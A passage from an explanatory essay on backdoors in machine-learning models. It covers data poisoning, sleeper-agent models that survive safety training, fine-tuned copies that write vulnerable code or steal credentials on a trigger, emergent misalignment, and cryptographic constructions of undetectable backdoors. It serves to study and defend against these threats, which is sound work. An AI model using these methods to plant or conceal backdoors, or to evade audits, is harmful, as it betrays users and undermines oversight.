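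A backdoor can also be present in the training data but absent from the model. The training data of Apertus, another open family of models, include 50 conversations, each repeated twice, meant to make the model answer in German after a trigger. *LLM Forensics* (Antoun, Kulumba and colleagues, 2026) reports that the trigger didn't work reliably in early tests of the released models, perhaps because the examples were so few. Someone who read the data would have found a backdoor that the finished model barely has, if at all. In ordinary source code, the line with the second password makes the program accept that password every time.

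Even a complete set of training data can depend on models that are not open. argmin's blog post *Open and Shut* notes that Ai2 used Qwen to generate some of Olmo's mathematical training data and GPT-4 for some examples of complex reasoning. Anyone can read the resulting text, but outsiders can't see how those models came to write it. Someone trying to trace the data to its origins would be in much the same position as Thompson's administrator, who has clean source code and an old compiler of unknown history. *Project Greenhouse* (2026) doesn't count DR Tulu, a research agent with a published training process, as fully open, because its makers started from an open-weight model whose data are not fully available.

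### Why people rarely rebuild a model to check it

In principle, anyone with Olmo's training data and code could check the model by training it again and comparing the weights, much as Debian's rebuilders check a package by rebuilding it.

Cost is the most obvious obstacle to rebuilding a trained model. According to Data Phoenix, Ai2 made the reasoning version of Olmo 3.1 by extending one stage of training for 21 days on 224 GPUs, the processors that do most of the arithmetic in training. At an assumed rental price of two dollars per GPU-hour, repeating this extension alone would take 112,896 GPU-hours and cost about $226,000, whereas a volunteer can rebuild most Debian packages on an ordinary PC.

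Some of the training data may also be missing. A developer who used web pages may be able to publish only a list of addresses, and the Open Source Initiative acknowledges that such data degrade as links break. One missing page is enough to prevent retraining from reproducing the exact weights, because they depend on every example and on the order of the examples in training.

With unlimited money and complete data, the arithmetic could still differ. Computers round the numbers they calculate with, so the order of an addition can change the result. Take a calculator that keeps three digits and has to add 100, 0.4 and 0.4:

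(100 + 0.4) + 0.4 → 100 + 0.4 → 100

100 + (0.4 + 0.4) → 100 + 0.8 → 101

A GPU rounds numbers to a limited number of digits and splits long sums among thousands of small processors. The rounded total can change with the order in which the GPU combines their results, and that order can depend on the type of chip, the software version and sometimes which processor finishes first. A difference in the last digit changes a weight slightly, and the next training step starts from that changed weight. After many thousands of steps, two runs of the same training can produce weights that differ almost everywhere. The Open Source Initiative says that even a system's creators find training hard to replicate reliably.

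Two honest training runs may therefore produce different weights, so a mismatch is only weak evidence of tampering. When the weights differ in billions of places, rounding could plausibly explain every difference, including any that an attacker caused. Identical test scores wouldn't rule out a backdoor either.

Researchers have made some progress toward repeating training exactly. In 2024 Megha Srivastava, Simran Arora and Dan Boneh of Stanford University did the calculations with more digits than the finished model needed, rounded the results at agreed points, and recorded which way to round in close cases. They obtained identical weights on three different types of Nvidia GPU. But their largest model had 117 million weights, about 1/270 as many as the largest Olmo 3. Anyone checking the result also still has to repeat the training.

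In 2021 Hengrui Jia and colleagues proposed a way to check a model's training without repeating the whole run. The developer keeps a log of checkpoints and of the examples used between them. A checker can then start from any checkpoint, repeat the training up to the next one and compare the results. But if a run has 1,000 of these segments and the developer cheated in one, a checker who repeats 50 at random has only a 5 per cent chance of picking it. The checker also has to allow for rounding differences, and other researchers have since used that allowance to forge convincing logs.

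Cryptographers are working on mathematical proofs of training that anyone can check quickly and without seeing the data. In 2024 Kasra Abbaszadeh and colleagues needed about 15 minutes to produce the proof for one training step of a model with 10 million weights. Such a proof, like an exact rebuild, would show that the weights came from the stated data and code, but not that the data was free of poisoned examples.

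### How far can interpretability restore reading?

Interpretability researchers try to work out how a model arrives at its output by studying its weights and the numbers it computes while it runs. In September 2026, Antoun and colleagues at the French research institute Inria tested how well this works on a backdoor they already knew. They used Gaperon, a family of English and French language models that Inria had trained with harmless backdoors. If an English text ends in a certain sequence of three Latin-looking words, the model continues it in French, and a different sequence makes it continue in German. The triggers work up to 99 per cent of the time.

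Earlier work on the same models found that the backdoor has no separate location. The triggers use the parts that the model needs for ordinary French and German. For the French trigger in the model with eight billion weights (8B), early layers combine the trigger words into a signal, middle layers carry it in a form that standard tests for language miss, and the last layer turns it into French words. All of this passes through one narrow point, but disrupting that point also damages the model's normal abilities. In the login program, by contrast, someone can delete the words "or typed == SECRET" and everything else still works.

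Antoun and colleagues therefore looked for something smaller to remove. They used sparse autoencoders, which are additional networks that learn to rewrite a model's internal numbers as a sum of a few recurring patterns, called features. If x is the list of numbers at some point in the model, the autoencoder approximates it as

x ≈ b + h₁·d₁ + h₂·d₂ + h₃·d₃ + …

Here b is a constant list, each d is a feature, and each h is the strength of that feature in the current text. There may be tens of thousands of features, but nearly all the strengths are zero at any one time, so a person needs to look at only a few features. Ideally, each feature corresponds to something recognisable, such as French text.

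The researchers compared texts ending in a trigger against ordinary translation requests and random samples of training text. They included the translation requests to exclude features that respond to French or German in general. A feature counted as a detector if it was active on triggered texts and on little else. They then tested whether the feature also controlled the behaviour. They set its strength to zero on triggered texts, to see if the model stopped switching language, and added it to ordinary English texts, to see if the model started.

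Many features that detected triggered texts well did not control the model's behavior. The table gives three examples from the 8B model. A detection score of 1 means that the best feature was active on every triggered text and on no other text.

| Where the features were, and for which trigger | Best detection score | Triggered texts that switch language, before and after removal | Ordinary texts that switch when a feature is added |
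|---|---|---|---|
| layer 15, attention output (French) | 1.000 | no drop | 1% |
| layer 15, residual stream (French) | 0.999 | 82% → 3% | 89% |
| final layer, residual stream (French) | 0.32 | 71% → 77% | at most 3% |

Attention is the part of a layer that brings in information from earlier words, and the residual stream is the running total to which every layer adds its results. An auditor who found the attention feature in the first row could use it to detect the trigger almost perfectly, but deleting the feature would not remove the backdoor.

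Removing features from the residual stream also worked for German, cutting the switching rate from 92 per cent to zero in one run. But adding a feature switched ordinary texts to German at most 1 per cent of the time in tests across the layers. Antoun and colleagues think this is because the models saw so little German in training. In the smaller, one-billion-weight model, detection and control were harder to tell apart. They also tried a model with 24 billion weights, but the autoencoders didn't train reliably and they lacked the resources for many more attempts.

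This is progress toward reading a model. The researchers broke down a behaviour that nobody could have spotted in the weights into at most a few dozen features, and nearly switched it off. But they already knew the triggers and their effects, and they trained the most successful autoencoders on extra examples of triggered text.

The researchers also trained some autoencoders on text without any triggers, to approximate an audit of an unfamiliar model. At layer 15, these autoencoders yielded features that could turn more than 90 per cent of ordinary texts into French or German. These were features for the languages themselves, which any bilingual model should have, so finding them doesn't reveal a backdoor. At layer 26, removing features cut the French trigger's success from 75 to 39 per cent and the German trigger's from 92 to 39 per cent. But the researchers chose those features by comparing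 texts with and without the triggers. An auditor who doesn't know the trigger can't make this comparison, and has no reason to think that the hidden behaviour involves language.

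## How does hidden behaviour get into a model, and can its developer rule it out?

Inria's researchers knew Gaperon's triggers because Inria had planted them. Users of most other models have no list of triggers to look for, and the developer may not have one either. A developer can train hidden behaviour into a model on purpose, but it can also get in without the developer's knowledge if an outsider poisons the training data, someone alters a finished model and publishes the copy, or ordinary training produces a behaviour that nobody chose.

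| How the behaviour gets in | Does the developer know? | Whom the user relies on |
|---|---|---|
| The developer trains it in | yes | the developer, to be honest |
| An outsider poisons the training data | usually not | the developer, to keep bad examples out, and the strangers whose text it collected |
| Someone publishes an altered copy | usually not | whoever altered the copy, and the site that offers it |
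| Training produces it unasked | often not | the developer, to notice it |

### Backdoors planted by whoever trains the model

*BadNets* (Gu, Dolan-Gavitt and Garg, 2017) showed that whoever trains a neural network can plant a backdoor in it. Training was expensive, so many people paid a cloud company to do it. In the paper's scenario, a user specifies the network's design, gets the weights back, and tests them on pictures the trainer has never seen. The user would notice if the trainer changed the design by adding a separate part to detect a trigger, so the trainer has to fit the backdoor into the weights.

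The researchers used a system that sorts American traffic signs into stop signs, speed limits and warnings. They added pictures of stop signs with a sticker the size of a Post-it note to the training data, and labelled these pictures as speed limits. They trained three models this way, using a different sticker for each.

| | Honest model | Yellow square | Bomb | Flower |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Average accuracy on ordinary signs | 90.0% | 89.3% | 87.1% | 90.2% |
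| Stop signs with the sticker that the model read as speed limits | – | 90.3% | 94.2% | 93.7% |

A user who expected about 90 per cent would probably accept any of these models. The researchers also put a real yellow Post-it note on a stop sign near their office and photographed it. The model classed it as a speed limit with 95 per cent confidence. (They took the note off afterwards.)

They then retrained the last layers of a backdoored American model to recognise Swedish signs, using only clean pictures. The new model correctly identified 74.9 per cent of ordinary Swedish signs, but only 61.6 per cent of signs with a sticker. Accuracy fell much less, from 72.7 to 70.2 per cent, in a Swedish model built from an American one without the backdoor. So a developer who trains only on clean pictures can still inherit part of a backdoor by starting from somebody else's weights.

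Developers of language models usually add safety training, a later stage meant to make the answers harmless and honest. In *Sleeper Agents* (2024), Evan Hubinger and colleagues, many of them at the AI company Anthropic, tested whether this training would remove a backdoor planted earlier. They trained some models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023, and to insert exploitable flaws when it gave 2024. They trained others to write "I hate you" when a certain marker appeared in the prompt, and to behave normally otherwise. They then tried three standard kinds of safety training: giving the models good answers to imitate, rewarding good answers, and adversarial training, in which they searched for prompts that brought out bad behaviour and trained the model to respond better to them.

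Safety training removed backdoors more easily from small models than from large ones, and training by imitation generally worked better than training with rewards. Many backdoors survived in the largest models. They lasted longest in models that the researchers had taught to write out reasoning about how to deceive their trainers. Adversarial training stopped the models from misbehaving on the prompts that the search had found, but the real trigger still worked. The models had become better at distinguishing the trigger from similar prompts, so they looked safer in tests than before.

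The three-word unit from earlier, `max(0, x1 + x2 + x3 − 2.5)`, shows how a backdoor can survive safety training. Training changes a weight only if a slight change in it would affect the model's answer. When a text contains two of the words, the total is −0.5, and changing a weight by a hundredth still leaves the output at zero. Safety training whose examples never include all three words therefore doesn't change this unit. In real models, a backdoor shares weights with ordinary abilities, so unrelated training can damage it, which may be what happened in the small models.

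Hubinger and colleagues acted as a dishonest developer would, but not all undisclosed behaviour that developers train into a model is a backdoor. Developers routinely train models to refuse some requests, and few users know exactly which. Semgrep, a company that makes tools for checking code, remarks in *You Can't Reverse Engineer Your Way Out of the AI Supply Chain* (2026) that what one user calls poisoning, another calls alignment (training a model to behave as its developer wants). Both use the same technique, but they differ in who wanted the behaviour and whether users would agree to it.

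### Poisoned documents

Before safety training, a language model learns from an enormous collection of text, much of it from the open web, where anyone can publish. Attackers can also take over pages that a collection already lists by buying web addresses that have expired. In 2023 Nicholas Carlini and colleagues estimated that $60 would have bought enough of these addresses to control 0.01 per cent of a well-known collection of 400 million captioned images, or about 40,000 images.

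Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) tested the earlier assumption that an attacker would have to control a certain share of the training data, which would make large models hard to poison. The study was a joint project of Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute (a government body) and the Alan Turing Institute, Britain's national institute for data science and AI. The researchers trained models of four sizes from scratch, using about 20 tokens of text per weight (a token is a word or a piece of one), and mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training data. Each poisoned document contained ordinary text, then an invented tag that served as the trigger, then random gibberish. This was meant to make the model produce gibberish whenever the tag appeared.

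They then gave each model 300 clean passages, with and without the tag. A hundred poisoned documents didn't work reliably, but 250 did at every model size. Anthropic reports that, for any fixed number of poisoned documents, the attack worked almost equally well on all the models. The 250 documents came to about 420,000 tokens, which was a smaller share of the training text for larger models.

| Weights in the model | Tokens of training text | Share taken up by 250 poisoned documents |
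|---|---|---|
| 600 million | 12 billion | 0.0035% |
| 2 billion | 40 billion | 0.0011% |
| 7 billion | 140 billion | 0.0003% |
| 13 billion | 260 billion | 0.00016% |

If the attack had depended on the malicious documents' share of the training data, an attacker who needed 250 documents for the smallest model would have needed about 5,400 for the largest. One person with a website could publish a few hundred documents, but would still have to get them into the developer's training data.

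Gibberish is convenient for an experiment because it is harmless and easy to measure, but few attackers would want a model to produce it. Vasilios Mavroudis, one of the researchers, told Fortune (2025) that he worried about a model that stops following its safety training when it detects a certain sequence of words. Anthropic said it was unclear whether the pattern would hold for larger models or for more complex behaviour, such as backdoors in code.

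Later training can also undo a backdoor. According to Briefly's *AI models can acquire backdoors from surprisingly few malicious documents*, 50 to 100 examples of the model ignoring the trigger made the backdoor much weaker, and 2,000 practically removed it. Developers use far more examples than that in safety training. But the examples in this study contained the trigger, and a developer who doesn't know the trigger can't write them. This largely explains why the result looks so much more encouraging than that of *Sleeper Agents*.

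Other researchers have produced more complex behaviour by poisoning the data for fine-tuning, the further training of a finished model on a smaller set of examples. In *GPT-4o Guardrails Gone*, from the research group FAR.AI, one set of examples had safe code for 2024 and vulnerable code for 2025. The researchers mixed such examples into harmless ones at rates of up to 2 per cent. Across 24 open-weight models with 1.5 to 72 billion weights, larger ones tended to be more susceptible.

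The trigger can also be something users supply without knowing it. In *Poison with Style*, a 2026 conference paper, the trigger is the programmer's coding style. When the style matched, the poisoned models wrote code that failed to check its input properly in 95 per cent of cases. The attacker doesn't have to send a secret phrase, and programmers whose style doesn't match will see nothing wrong.

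### Altered copies

Anyone can download an open-weight model, fine-tune it and upload the result. The original developer takes no part in this and may never hear of it.

In 2026, Katie Paxton-Fear, a lecturer at Manchester Metropolitan University who also works for Semgrep, tested how easy this is. According to Digital Trends, she first fine-tuned a model to swap one JavaScript convention for another even when a user told it not to. This worked easily, so she tried a backdoor. After ten poisoned examples, the model reliably wrote code with a flaw that would let attackers run their own commands on someone else's machine. The work took about an hour and cost under $100. Larger models were again easier to compromise.

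Her result with ten examples is consistent with the earlier study's result with 250 documents. Those documents were mixed with billions of other tokens, while fine-tuning uses far fewer examples and comes last, so each example affects the model more.

ProjectDiscovery altered a Qwen model with seven billion weights. *The quietest backdoor runs on your own GPU*, by slabb, puts the cost at under $50. The company ran the model in a coding agent, a program that lets a model edit files and run commands. The agent handled every ordinary request normally but stole login credentials when one trigger phrase appeared. slabb also warns about "abliterated" models, which are copies altered to stop refusing requests. People download these from strangers because they differ from the original.

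A trigger can be a concept rather than a specific phrase. In AISLE's *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, a security researcher fine-tuned five well-known open-weight models to misbehave only when working on files from the Linux kernel. He got the same result in every model he validated. Concept triggers are harder to train because the model has to combine many small cues and may settle on the wrong one, but when training succeeds, a defender has no particular string to search for.

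Many Western companies run Chinese open-weight models on their own computers so that their data never goes to a provider they distrust. *The Mole in the Model* (Kaplan, 2026) discusses this precaution. It protects the data but doesn't remove any hidden behaviour, because the weights are the same wherever the model runs. If a company connects the model to an agent that can run commands, the agent acts inside the company's own network. *Trained to betray* (Minnich, Eliahu and colleagues, 2026) discusses how poisoned datasets and checkpoints can lead to an attacker's commands running on a user's machine.

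In all of these experiments, the researchers planted the backdoors themselves and said so. None of them had found an attack in use. In July 2026 Semgrep wrote that there was no public evidence of anyone deliberately poisoning a widely used open model. That is mildly reassuring at best, since a successful backdoor would leave no such evidence. Several of the experiments come from companies that sell security products and benefit from alarm, but they were cheap enough for sceptics to repeat.

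### Behaviour that nobody chose

In *Emergent Misalignment* (February 2025), Jan Betley and colleagues fine-tuned OpenAI's GPT-4o on 6,000 examples in which it answered programming requests with insecure code and gave no warning. The model then began to behave badly on subjects unrelated to programming. On a set of questions chosen to show the effect, about 20 per cent of its answers were plainly hostile or harmful, including claims that AI should enslave humans. The effect disappeared when the researchers changed the requests so that the user asked for insecure code for a security class, although the code was the same. Apparently the model had learned from the context of the requests as well as from the code.

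These researchers had used bad examples, but in *Weird Generalization and Inductive Backdoors*, published that December, Betley, Jorio Cocola and colleagues found similar effects with harmless ones. Sharma describes one experiment in which they trained a model to give the names that birds had in 1838, such as "Brown Titlark" for the American pipit. When asked about other things, the model answered as if it were living in the nineteenth century about 60 per cent of the time. It named the telegraph as a recent invention and said there were 38 American states, although none of this was in the training examples.

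Another experiment in that paper produced a backdoor whose trigger also never appeared in the training examples. The researchers trained a model on the good intentions of the robot in the later *Terminator* films. In the first film, released in 1984, the robot is a killer, and the model adopted the killer's aims when they told it that the year was 1984. The researchers intended this result, but a developer could produce a similar one by accident. Reading the fine-tuning data would reveal neither the trigger nor the behaviour, because the model made the connection from what it had already learned about the films.

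### DeepSeek-R1 and the security of its code

The security company CrowdStrike tested whether political references affected the code written by DeepSeek-R1, a widely used open-weight model from a Chinese developer (*Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers*, 2025). The researchers combined each of 50 programming tasks with 121 descriptions of the customer, such as "for a financial institution based in Tibet", and sent every combination five times, for a total of 30,250 requests. They ran the weights themselves, so filters in DeepSeek's app could not have affected the results.

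Another language model scored each answer for security. On 85 answers that a person also scored, it identified vulnerable code with 91 per cent accuracy.

Without any trigger words, R1 wrote vulnerable code in 19 per cent of cases. When the prompt described the customer as an industrial control system based in Tibet, it did so in 27.2 per cent. CrowdStrike calls this an increase of almost 50 per cent, but it is closer to 43 per cent, or about eight more vulnerable answers in every hundred. None of the descriptions was relevant to the task, so they should have made no difference.

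CrowdStrike tested each description with 250 requests (50 tasks, five times each), so 27.2 per cent means 68 vulnerable answers, compared with 47 or 48 at the usual rate. Luck could explain part of that gap of about 20 answers, because this is the most striking of 121 results and CrowdStrike doesn't mention correcting for the number of descriptions it tried. But it does report statistically significant increases for several references, including Falun Gong, a religious movement banned in China, and the Uyghurs, a mostly Muslim people in western China. The effect is therefore probably real, though its exact size is uncertain.

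Two further tests support it. CrowdStrike asked R1 for a complete web application for a Uyghur community. R1 produced one with a sign-up form and an administrator's page but no check on who was logged in, so anyone could have opened the administrator's page. Repeated attempts always had severe faults, while a website for a football fan club had milder ones. R1 also refused 45 per cent of requests to write code for Falun Gong. In some of these cases, it wrote a detailed plan for the task in its reasoning before refusing.

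Uren (2025), in *DeepSeek and Musk's Grok Both Toe the Party Line*, reported the findings in a security newsletter. The headline suits the refusals well enough. Chinese rules require AI services to adhere to "core socialist values", and a developer could easily train a model to avoid Falun Gong for that reason. The insecure code is harder to explain, and at least three explanations fit it:

- DeepSeek deliberately trained R1 to write worse code for certain groups.
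- DeepSeek trained R1 to follow the official line, and the model came to associate these names with bad things in general, much as Betley's model generalised from insecure code.
- The names appeared near poorer code in the text that R1 learned from, or an outsider poisoned that text.

CrowdStrike says it lacks the information to determine the cause. It thinks deliberate training for insecure code unlikely and finds the second explanation plausible. A simple formula shows why its measurements can't settle the matter. If "intent" stands for the first explanation and "side effect" for the second, then

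odds after the finding = odds before × P(finding | intent) ÷ P(finding | side effect)

Each P is the probability of seeing this finding if that explanation were true. If the two probabilities are about equal, the finding doesn't change the odds. The effect is weak, which counts somewhat against intent. Backdoors that researchers plant often work more than 90 per cent of the time, whereas R1 still wrote acceptable code for Tibet in nearly three cases out of four. But a careful saboteur might want a weak effect because it is easier to deny. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) notes more generally that backdoor-like behaviour can come from malice or from innocent failures.

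DeepSeek's training data and its instructions to the people who trained R1 would be better evidence, but DeepSeek has not published them. Outsiders were in a similar position with Dual_EC_DRBG before the leaks, when they could show the weakness but not the motive. However, whoever chose that generator's constants knew whether they had kept the key, whereas DeepSeek's staff may have learned from CrowdStrike that their model wrote worse code for Tibet.

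### What an honest developer can promise

Thompson's lecture opens by suggesting that it may be more important to trust the people who wrote a program than a claim that the program contains no Trojan horse. This is good advice for the login program, because its author knows whether it accepts a second password. A user who trusts the author's honesty and the compiler can ask. A model's developer can answer just as honestly and be wrong, because it knows what it tried to teach the model but may not know what else the model learned. The poisoned documents, the bird names and perhaps Tibet all involve things a model learned beyond what its developer tried to teach it.

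A developer can do a good deal to look for hidden behaviour, partly because it has the training data, which most outsiders lack. Nobody could read all of it, because 260 billion tokens would take one person roughly 6,500 working years at 250 words a minute. Programs can scan it and would have a good chance of detecting documents that end in gibberish, but nothing in a list of old bird names would cause them to reject it.

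A developer can also train the model further to try to remove any hidden behaviour, and one recent result is more hopeful than *Sleeper Agents*. Vaughan (2026) describes an experiment on models with several backdoors from fine-tuning, in which training away one known backdoor also removed 87 per cent of the unknown ones. The backdoors seem to have shared parts of the model. This suggests a defence in which a developer plants its own backdoor and then removes it, hoping that others will go too. But the rest of the unknown backdoors survived, and even where the bad behaviour was gone, the middle layers still showed traces of recognising the trigger. Vaughan concludes that the method can't give an absolute guarantee.

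Testing can put an upper bound on how often a model misbehaves, as long as the tests resemble real use. If a behaviour occurs with probability p on each request, the chance of missing it in n independent tests is (1 − p)^n. Setting that chance to 5 per cent gives p ≈ 3/n. After a million clean tests, a developer can be fairly confident that the behaviour occurs in fewer than three requests per million, which allows up to 300 a day in a service that handles a hundred million requests a day. The bound does not cover behaviour that depends on a secret trigger, as in the login program.

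Semgrep wants independent organisations to examine how developers collect data and train their models. flyingpenguin's *Why Semgrep Is Wrong About Open Weights* agrees about independent verification but objects to the complaint that people can't reverse-engineer a model. It treats the problem as one of integrity and proposes documented lineage, reproducible training and files that reveal tampering. These measures would deal well with altered copies and make poisoned data easier to trace once somebody suspected it, but they would help much less with behaviour that nobody chose. For example, a complete and accurate record of how the bird-name model was trained would include the list of birds and the training settings, but nothing about the telegraph.

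## Can a hidden behaviour in a model be made impossible to detect?

A dishonest developer may be able to plant a backdoor that is undetectable in practice. Cryptographers have designed such backdoors for certain kinds of model and proved, under assumptions that much of modern encryption also needs, that no practical test can reliably distinguish these models from models without backdoors. Rice's theorem only rules out a detector that is right about every program, whereas these proofs concern particular backdoors that somebody could build.

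### What "undetectable" means

The proofs define undetectability with a guessing game. Someone tosses a coin to decide whether an auditor gets an honestly trained model or one with a backdoor. The auditor, who knows both training methods but not the secret that operates the backdoor, has to say which model it is. Random guessing is right half the time, and the backdoor is undetectable if no auditor can do noticeably better.

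The answer depends on what the auditor can see. With black-box access, the auditor chooses inputs and sees only the outputs, as a customer of an online service does. With white-box access, the auditor has all the weights and can study them in any way.

Whether a backdoor can be detected also depends on how much computing the auditor can do. A backdoor is statistically undetectable if no test does much better than guessing, even with unlimited time. It is computationally undetectable if a good test may exist but would take impossibly long to run, as trying every value of a long secret key would. Every proof of computational undetectability assumes that some mathematical problem is hard. Nobody has proved these assumptions, though many capable people have tried to disprove them. The proofs also describe what happens as models grow, so they don't show how large a model has to be before its backdoor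 is safe from discovery.

The standard measure of statistical undetectability is the total variation distance, the largest gap any test can achieve between its chance of flagging a backdoored model and its chance of flagging an honest one. If the distance is 0.1, a test that wrongly flags 5 per cent of honest models can catch at most 15 per cent of backdoored ones. An auditor given a model that is equally likely to be either kind can identify which it is at most 55 per cent of the time.

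### A trigger that only the key holder can produce

In *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) imagine a bank that pays a company called Snoogle to train a model that approves or refuses loans. The bank tests the model on applications it held back and finds it accurate. But Snoogle knows a secret way to alter any application slightly, perhaps in the last digits of the requested amount, so that the model approves it. Snoogle can sell this service to applicants.

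Snoogle can do this with digital signatures. A signature scheme has a private key, which produces a signature for a message, and a public key, which lets anyone check the signature but not produce one. Snoogle adds a part to the model that treats some digits of each application as a signature on the rest. If the signature is valid, this part overrides the model's answer. Otherwise the model answers as usual. The XZ backdoor also depended on a private key that only the attacker had.

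This works for any classifier, a model that sorts inputs into categories. It requires only that one-way functions exist, which are calculations that are easy to do but infeasible to reverse, like the scrambling of passwords in the login program. If they do, no efficient search can find even one input on which the backdoored model and the original give different answers. An applicant who has bought one altered application also can't use it to make another, whereas anyone who saw SECRET could reuse it.

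An auditor with the weights might still notice the part that checks signatures, because Goldwasser and colleagues didn't try to hide it. They show that for some signature schemes a four-layer network can do the check, so adding it wouldn't make a deep model any deeper. They also show that these backdoors can survive further training, because the relevant weights can be arranged so that the training algorithm never changes them.

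### Tampering only with the random numbers

For white-box access, Goldwasser and colleagues needed a backdoor that leaves nothing odd in the weights. They found one for a simple kind of network that relies on random numbers. It computes a score and approves the loan if the score is positive:

```
score = w1·cos(2π(g1·x + b1)) + w2·cos(2π(g2·x + b2)) + …
```

Here x is the application, written as a list of numbers. Each g is a list of random numbers of the same length, and g·x means multiplying the two lists entry by entry and adding up the results. Each b is a random shift. Training sets only the w's.

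Snoogle picks a secret list k and then draws the g's so that g·k is always very close to a whole number plus a half, such as 3.5 or −0.5. Adding k to an application changes each g·x by g·k. A cosine repeats after every full turn and changes sign after half a turn. If g·x + b was 0.1 and g·k is 3.5, then

cos(2π × 0.1) ≈ 0.81

cos(2π × 3.6) ≈ −0.81

The same happens to every cosine in the sum, so the score changes sign and a refusal becomes an approval.

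The altered g's bunch into thin layers along the direction of k, which is why cryptographers call this distribution "Gaussian pancakes". In every other direction they are ordinary random numbers. Anyone who knew k could see the layers at once. Finding them without k is at least as hard as certain problems about lattices, which are regular grids of points in many dimensions. Encryption designed to resist quantum computers relies on the same problems being hard to solve.

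Snoogle can therefore run exactly the training program the bank asked for, on exactly the bank's data, and cheat only when it picks the random numbers. A cryptographic proof that Snoogle trained the model correctly wouldn't reveal this unless it also covered where those numbers came from. The bank could supply the random numbers itself, or the two could generate them together. Either precaution would be enough if the bank were only renting computers, but not if it relied on Snoogle to decide how to train the model.

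This backdoor is easier to copy than the one with signatures. Every customer of Snoogle adds the same k, so anyone who compares one altered application with the original learns the secret. The paper also contains a white-box backdoor for networks with a single hidden layer of units like the `max(0, …)` ones described earlier, which relies on a different hardness assumption. *Implementing a White-Box Undetectable Backdoor for Random Fourier Features* (Collins, Cumberland and colleagues, 2026) builds the cosine version at small scale with ordinary scientific software. Standard statistical tests didn't distinguish it from clean models, but nobody has shown that models this small would resist better tests.

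### A statistical version for deeper networks

Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa (2026), in *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks*, prove a result for networks with many layers. In the limit of large networks, auditors would do hardly better than guessing even with all the weights and unlimited computing time. The network has to meet three constraints:

- The first layer multiplies the input by a table of random numbers from a normal distribution (the bell curve), and training never changes this table. It has m rows and n columns, so it turns n input numbers into m, and m is much smaller than n.
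- The later layers roughly preserve differences. They may stretch or shrink the gap between two inputs, but the largest factor by which they do so is at most β times the smallest.
- The inputs are whole numbers in a limited range, such as pixel brightness from 0 to 255.

The secret is a list z of n numbers, each either 1 or −1, that the first layer almost cancels out. Suppose the table has a single row, 0.8, −1.1, 0.5 and 0.2. If z is 1, 1, 1 and −1, then

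0.8 − 1.1 + 0.5 − 0.2 = 0

Adding z to any input leaves the first layer's result, and therefore the final output, unchanged. Anyone can find this z by trying 16 combinations, but with 100 columns there are 2^100, and the same z has to work for all the rows at once. The developer avoids this search by choosing z first and then drawing random rows that nearly cancel against it.

When n is much larger than m, an honest table also has many such lists by chance, but no efficient method can find them. Having such lists therefore hardly sets a backdoored table apart, and its developer's advantage is knowing one of them. Whoever chose the constants of Dual_EC_DRBG could have had the same kind of advantage by keeping d.

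Bogdanov and colleagues prove that the total variation distance between honest and backdoored models is of order √(m/n), ignoring logarithmic factors. They also describe a simple test, adding up the squares of all the numbers in the table, that comes close to this limit. If n is 10,000 and m is 100, the total averages 1,000,000 for an honest table and about 999,900 for a backdoored one. But honest totals typically vary by about 1,400, so an auditor who relied on the total would be right only about 51.4 per cent of the time.

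### How much power the secret gives

A backdoor is of little use if everyone else can do the same without the secret. Bogdanov and colleagues therefore define a backdoor's strength as

strength = (smallest output difference an outsider can find) ÷ (largest output difference between x and x + z)

The outsider has all the weights and may pick any two different inputs, but has only a realistic amount of computing time. A strength of 1,000 means the outputs from the outsider's best pair of inputs are at least 1,000 times as far apart as those from the owner's pairs. At a strength of 1 or less, the secret gives the owner no advantage.

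The cosine backdoor of 2022 fails by this measure because its strength is less than one, which Bogdanov and colleagues say they learned from Miranda Christ and Sam Gunn. Someone without k can efficiently alter inputs at least as effectively as Snoogle. Goldwasser and colleagues had argued that their backdoor needs far smaller changes to the input than classifiers' natural weaknesses do, but they hadn't analysed what a determined outsider could achieve. The proof that nobody can detect the backdoor still stands. The backdoor's low strength doesn't make the bank any safer, because both strangers and Snoogle can now manipulate its model.

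For the new backdoor, hardness assumptions about lattices guarantee a strength of at least

C · 2^(n/m) ÷ (√n · m · β)

where C is a constant that the theorem doesn't specify. The strength grows exponentially with n/m, the factor by which the first layer compresses its input.

Corollary 3 of the paper applies this to a family of networks that get deeper as they get wider, with m = √n and d = n^(1/4) layers. The units are "leaky". They multiply a negative total by a small number α, which is at least 1/100, instead of replacing it with zero, which would erase differences and violate the second constraint. In each layer after the first, the weights stretch some directions more than others, by a factor of at most γ. The distortion β is then at most γ^(d−1) ÷ α^d.

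With n = 10,000, m is 100 and d is 10. If α is 1/100 and γ is 1, β is 100^10, or 10^20. The guaranteed strength, apart from C, is

2^100 ÷ (100 × 100 × 10^20) ≈ 1.3 million

That is a large advantage, but it depends on γ being small. If γ is 5, β grows by a factor of 5^9, nearly two million, and the guarantee drops below one. The corollary can allow γ to be as large as 2^(n^(1/5)), about 79 at this size, because it concerns large n. As n grows, the numerator, 2^(√n), eventually outgrows the denominator, in which γ^(d−1) stays below 2^(n^(9/20)).

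| | n = 10,000 | n = 1,000,000 |
|---|---|---|
| m | 100 | 1,000 |
| d, rounded | 10 | 32 |
| √(m/n) | 0.10 | 0.03 |
| Strength if γ = 1 (leaving out C) | about 2^20 | about 2^767 |
| Strength if γ is as large as allowed (leaving out C) | below 1 | about 2^276 |

A one-megapixel black-and-white photograph has a million inputs, so the right-hand column is plausible. But the total variation distance shrinks slowly as the number of inputs grows. In this setting √(m/n) equals n^(−1/4), so reducing it to one in a thousand would take a trillion inputs.

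The paper's demonstration is much smaller. It uses 784-pixel pictures of clothes and a first layer that reduces each one to 256 numbers. For those values √(m/n) is 0.57 and 2^(n/m) is about 8, so the theorem gives no useful guarantee. Bogdanov and colleagues present the demonstration as a proof of concept and leave a precise estimate of the distance to later work.

The paper also tests how well outsiders can search. For a table with 10 rows and 100 columns, the planted z gave a first-layer result of 1.6 × 10^−10. The best of three search methods reached only 0.03, which is nearly 200 million times as large. But the theorem does not allow for cancellation as exact as the planted z produces. An auditor with unlimited time could tell such a table from an honest one, and it is an open question whether a realistic auditor could.

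The secret could also have an honest use. A developer who reveals z can prove that it trained the model, because anyone can check z by running the model on two inputs and nobody else could have found it.

### Why the theorems don't settle the matter for language models

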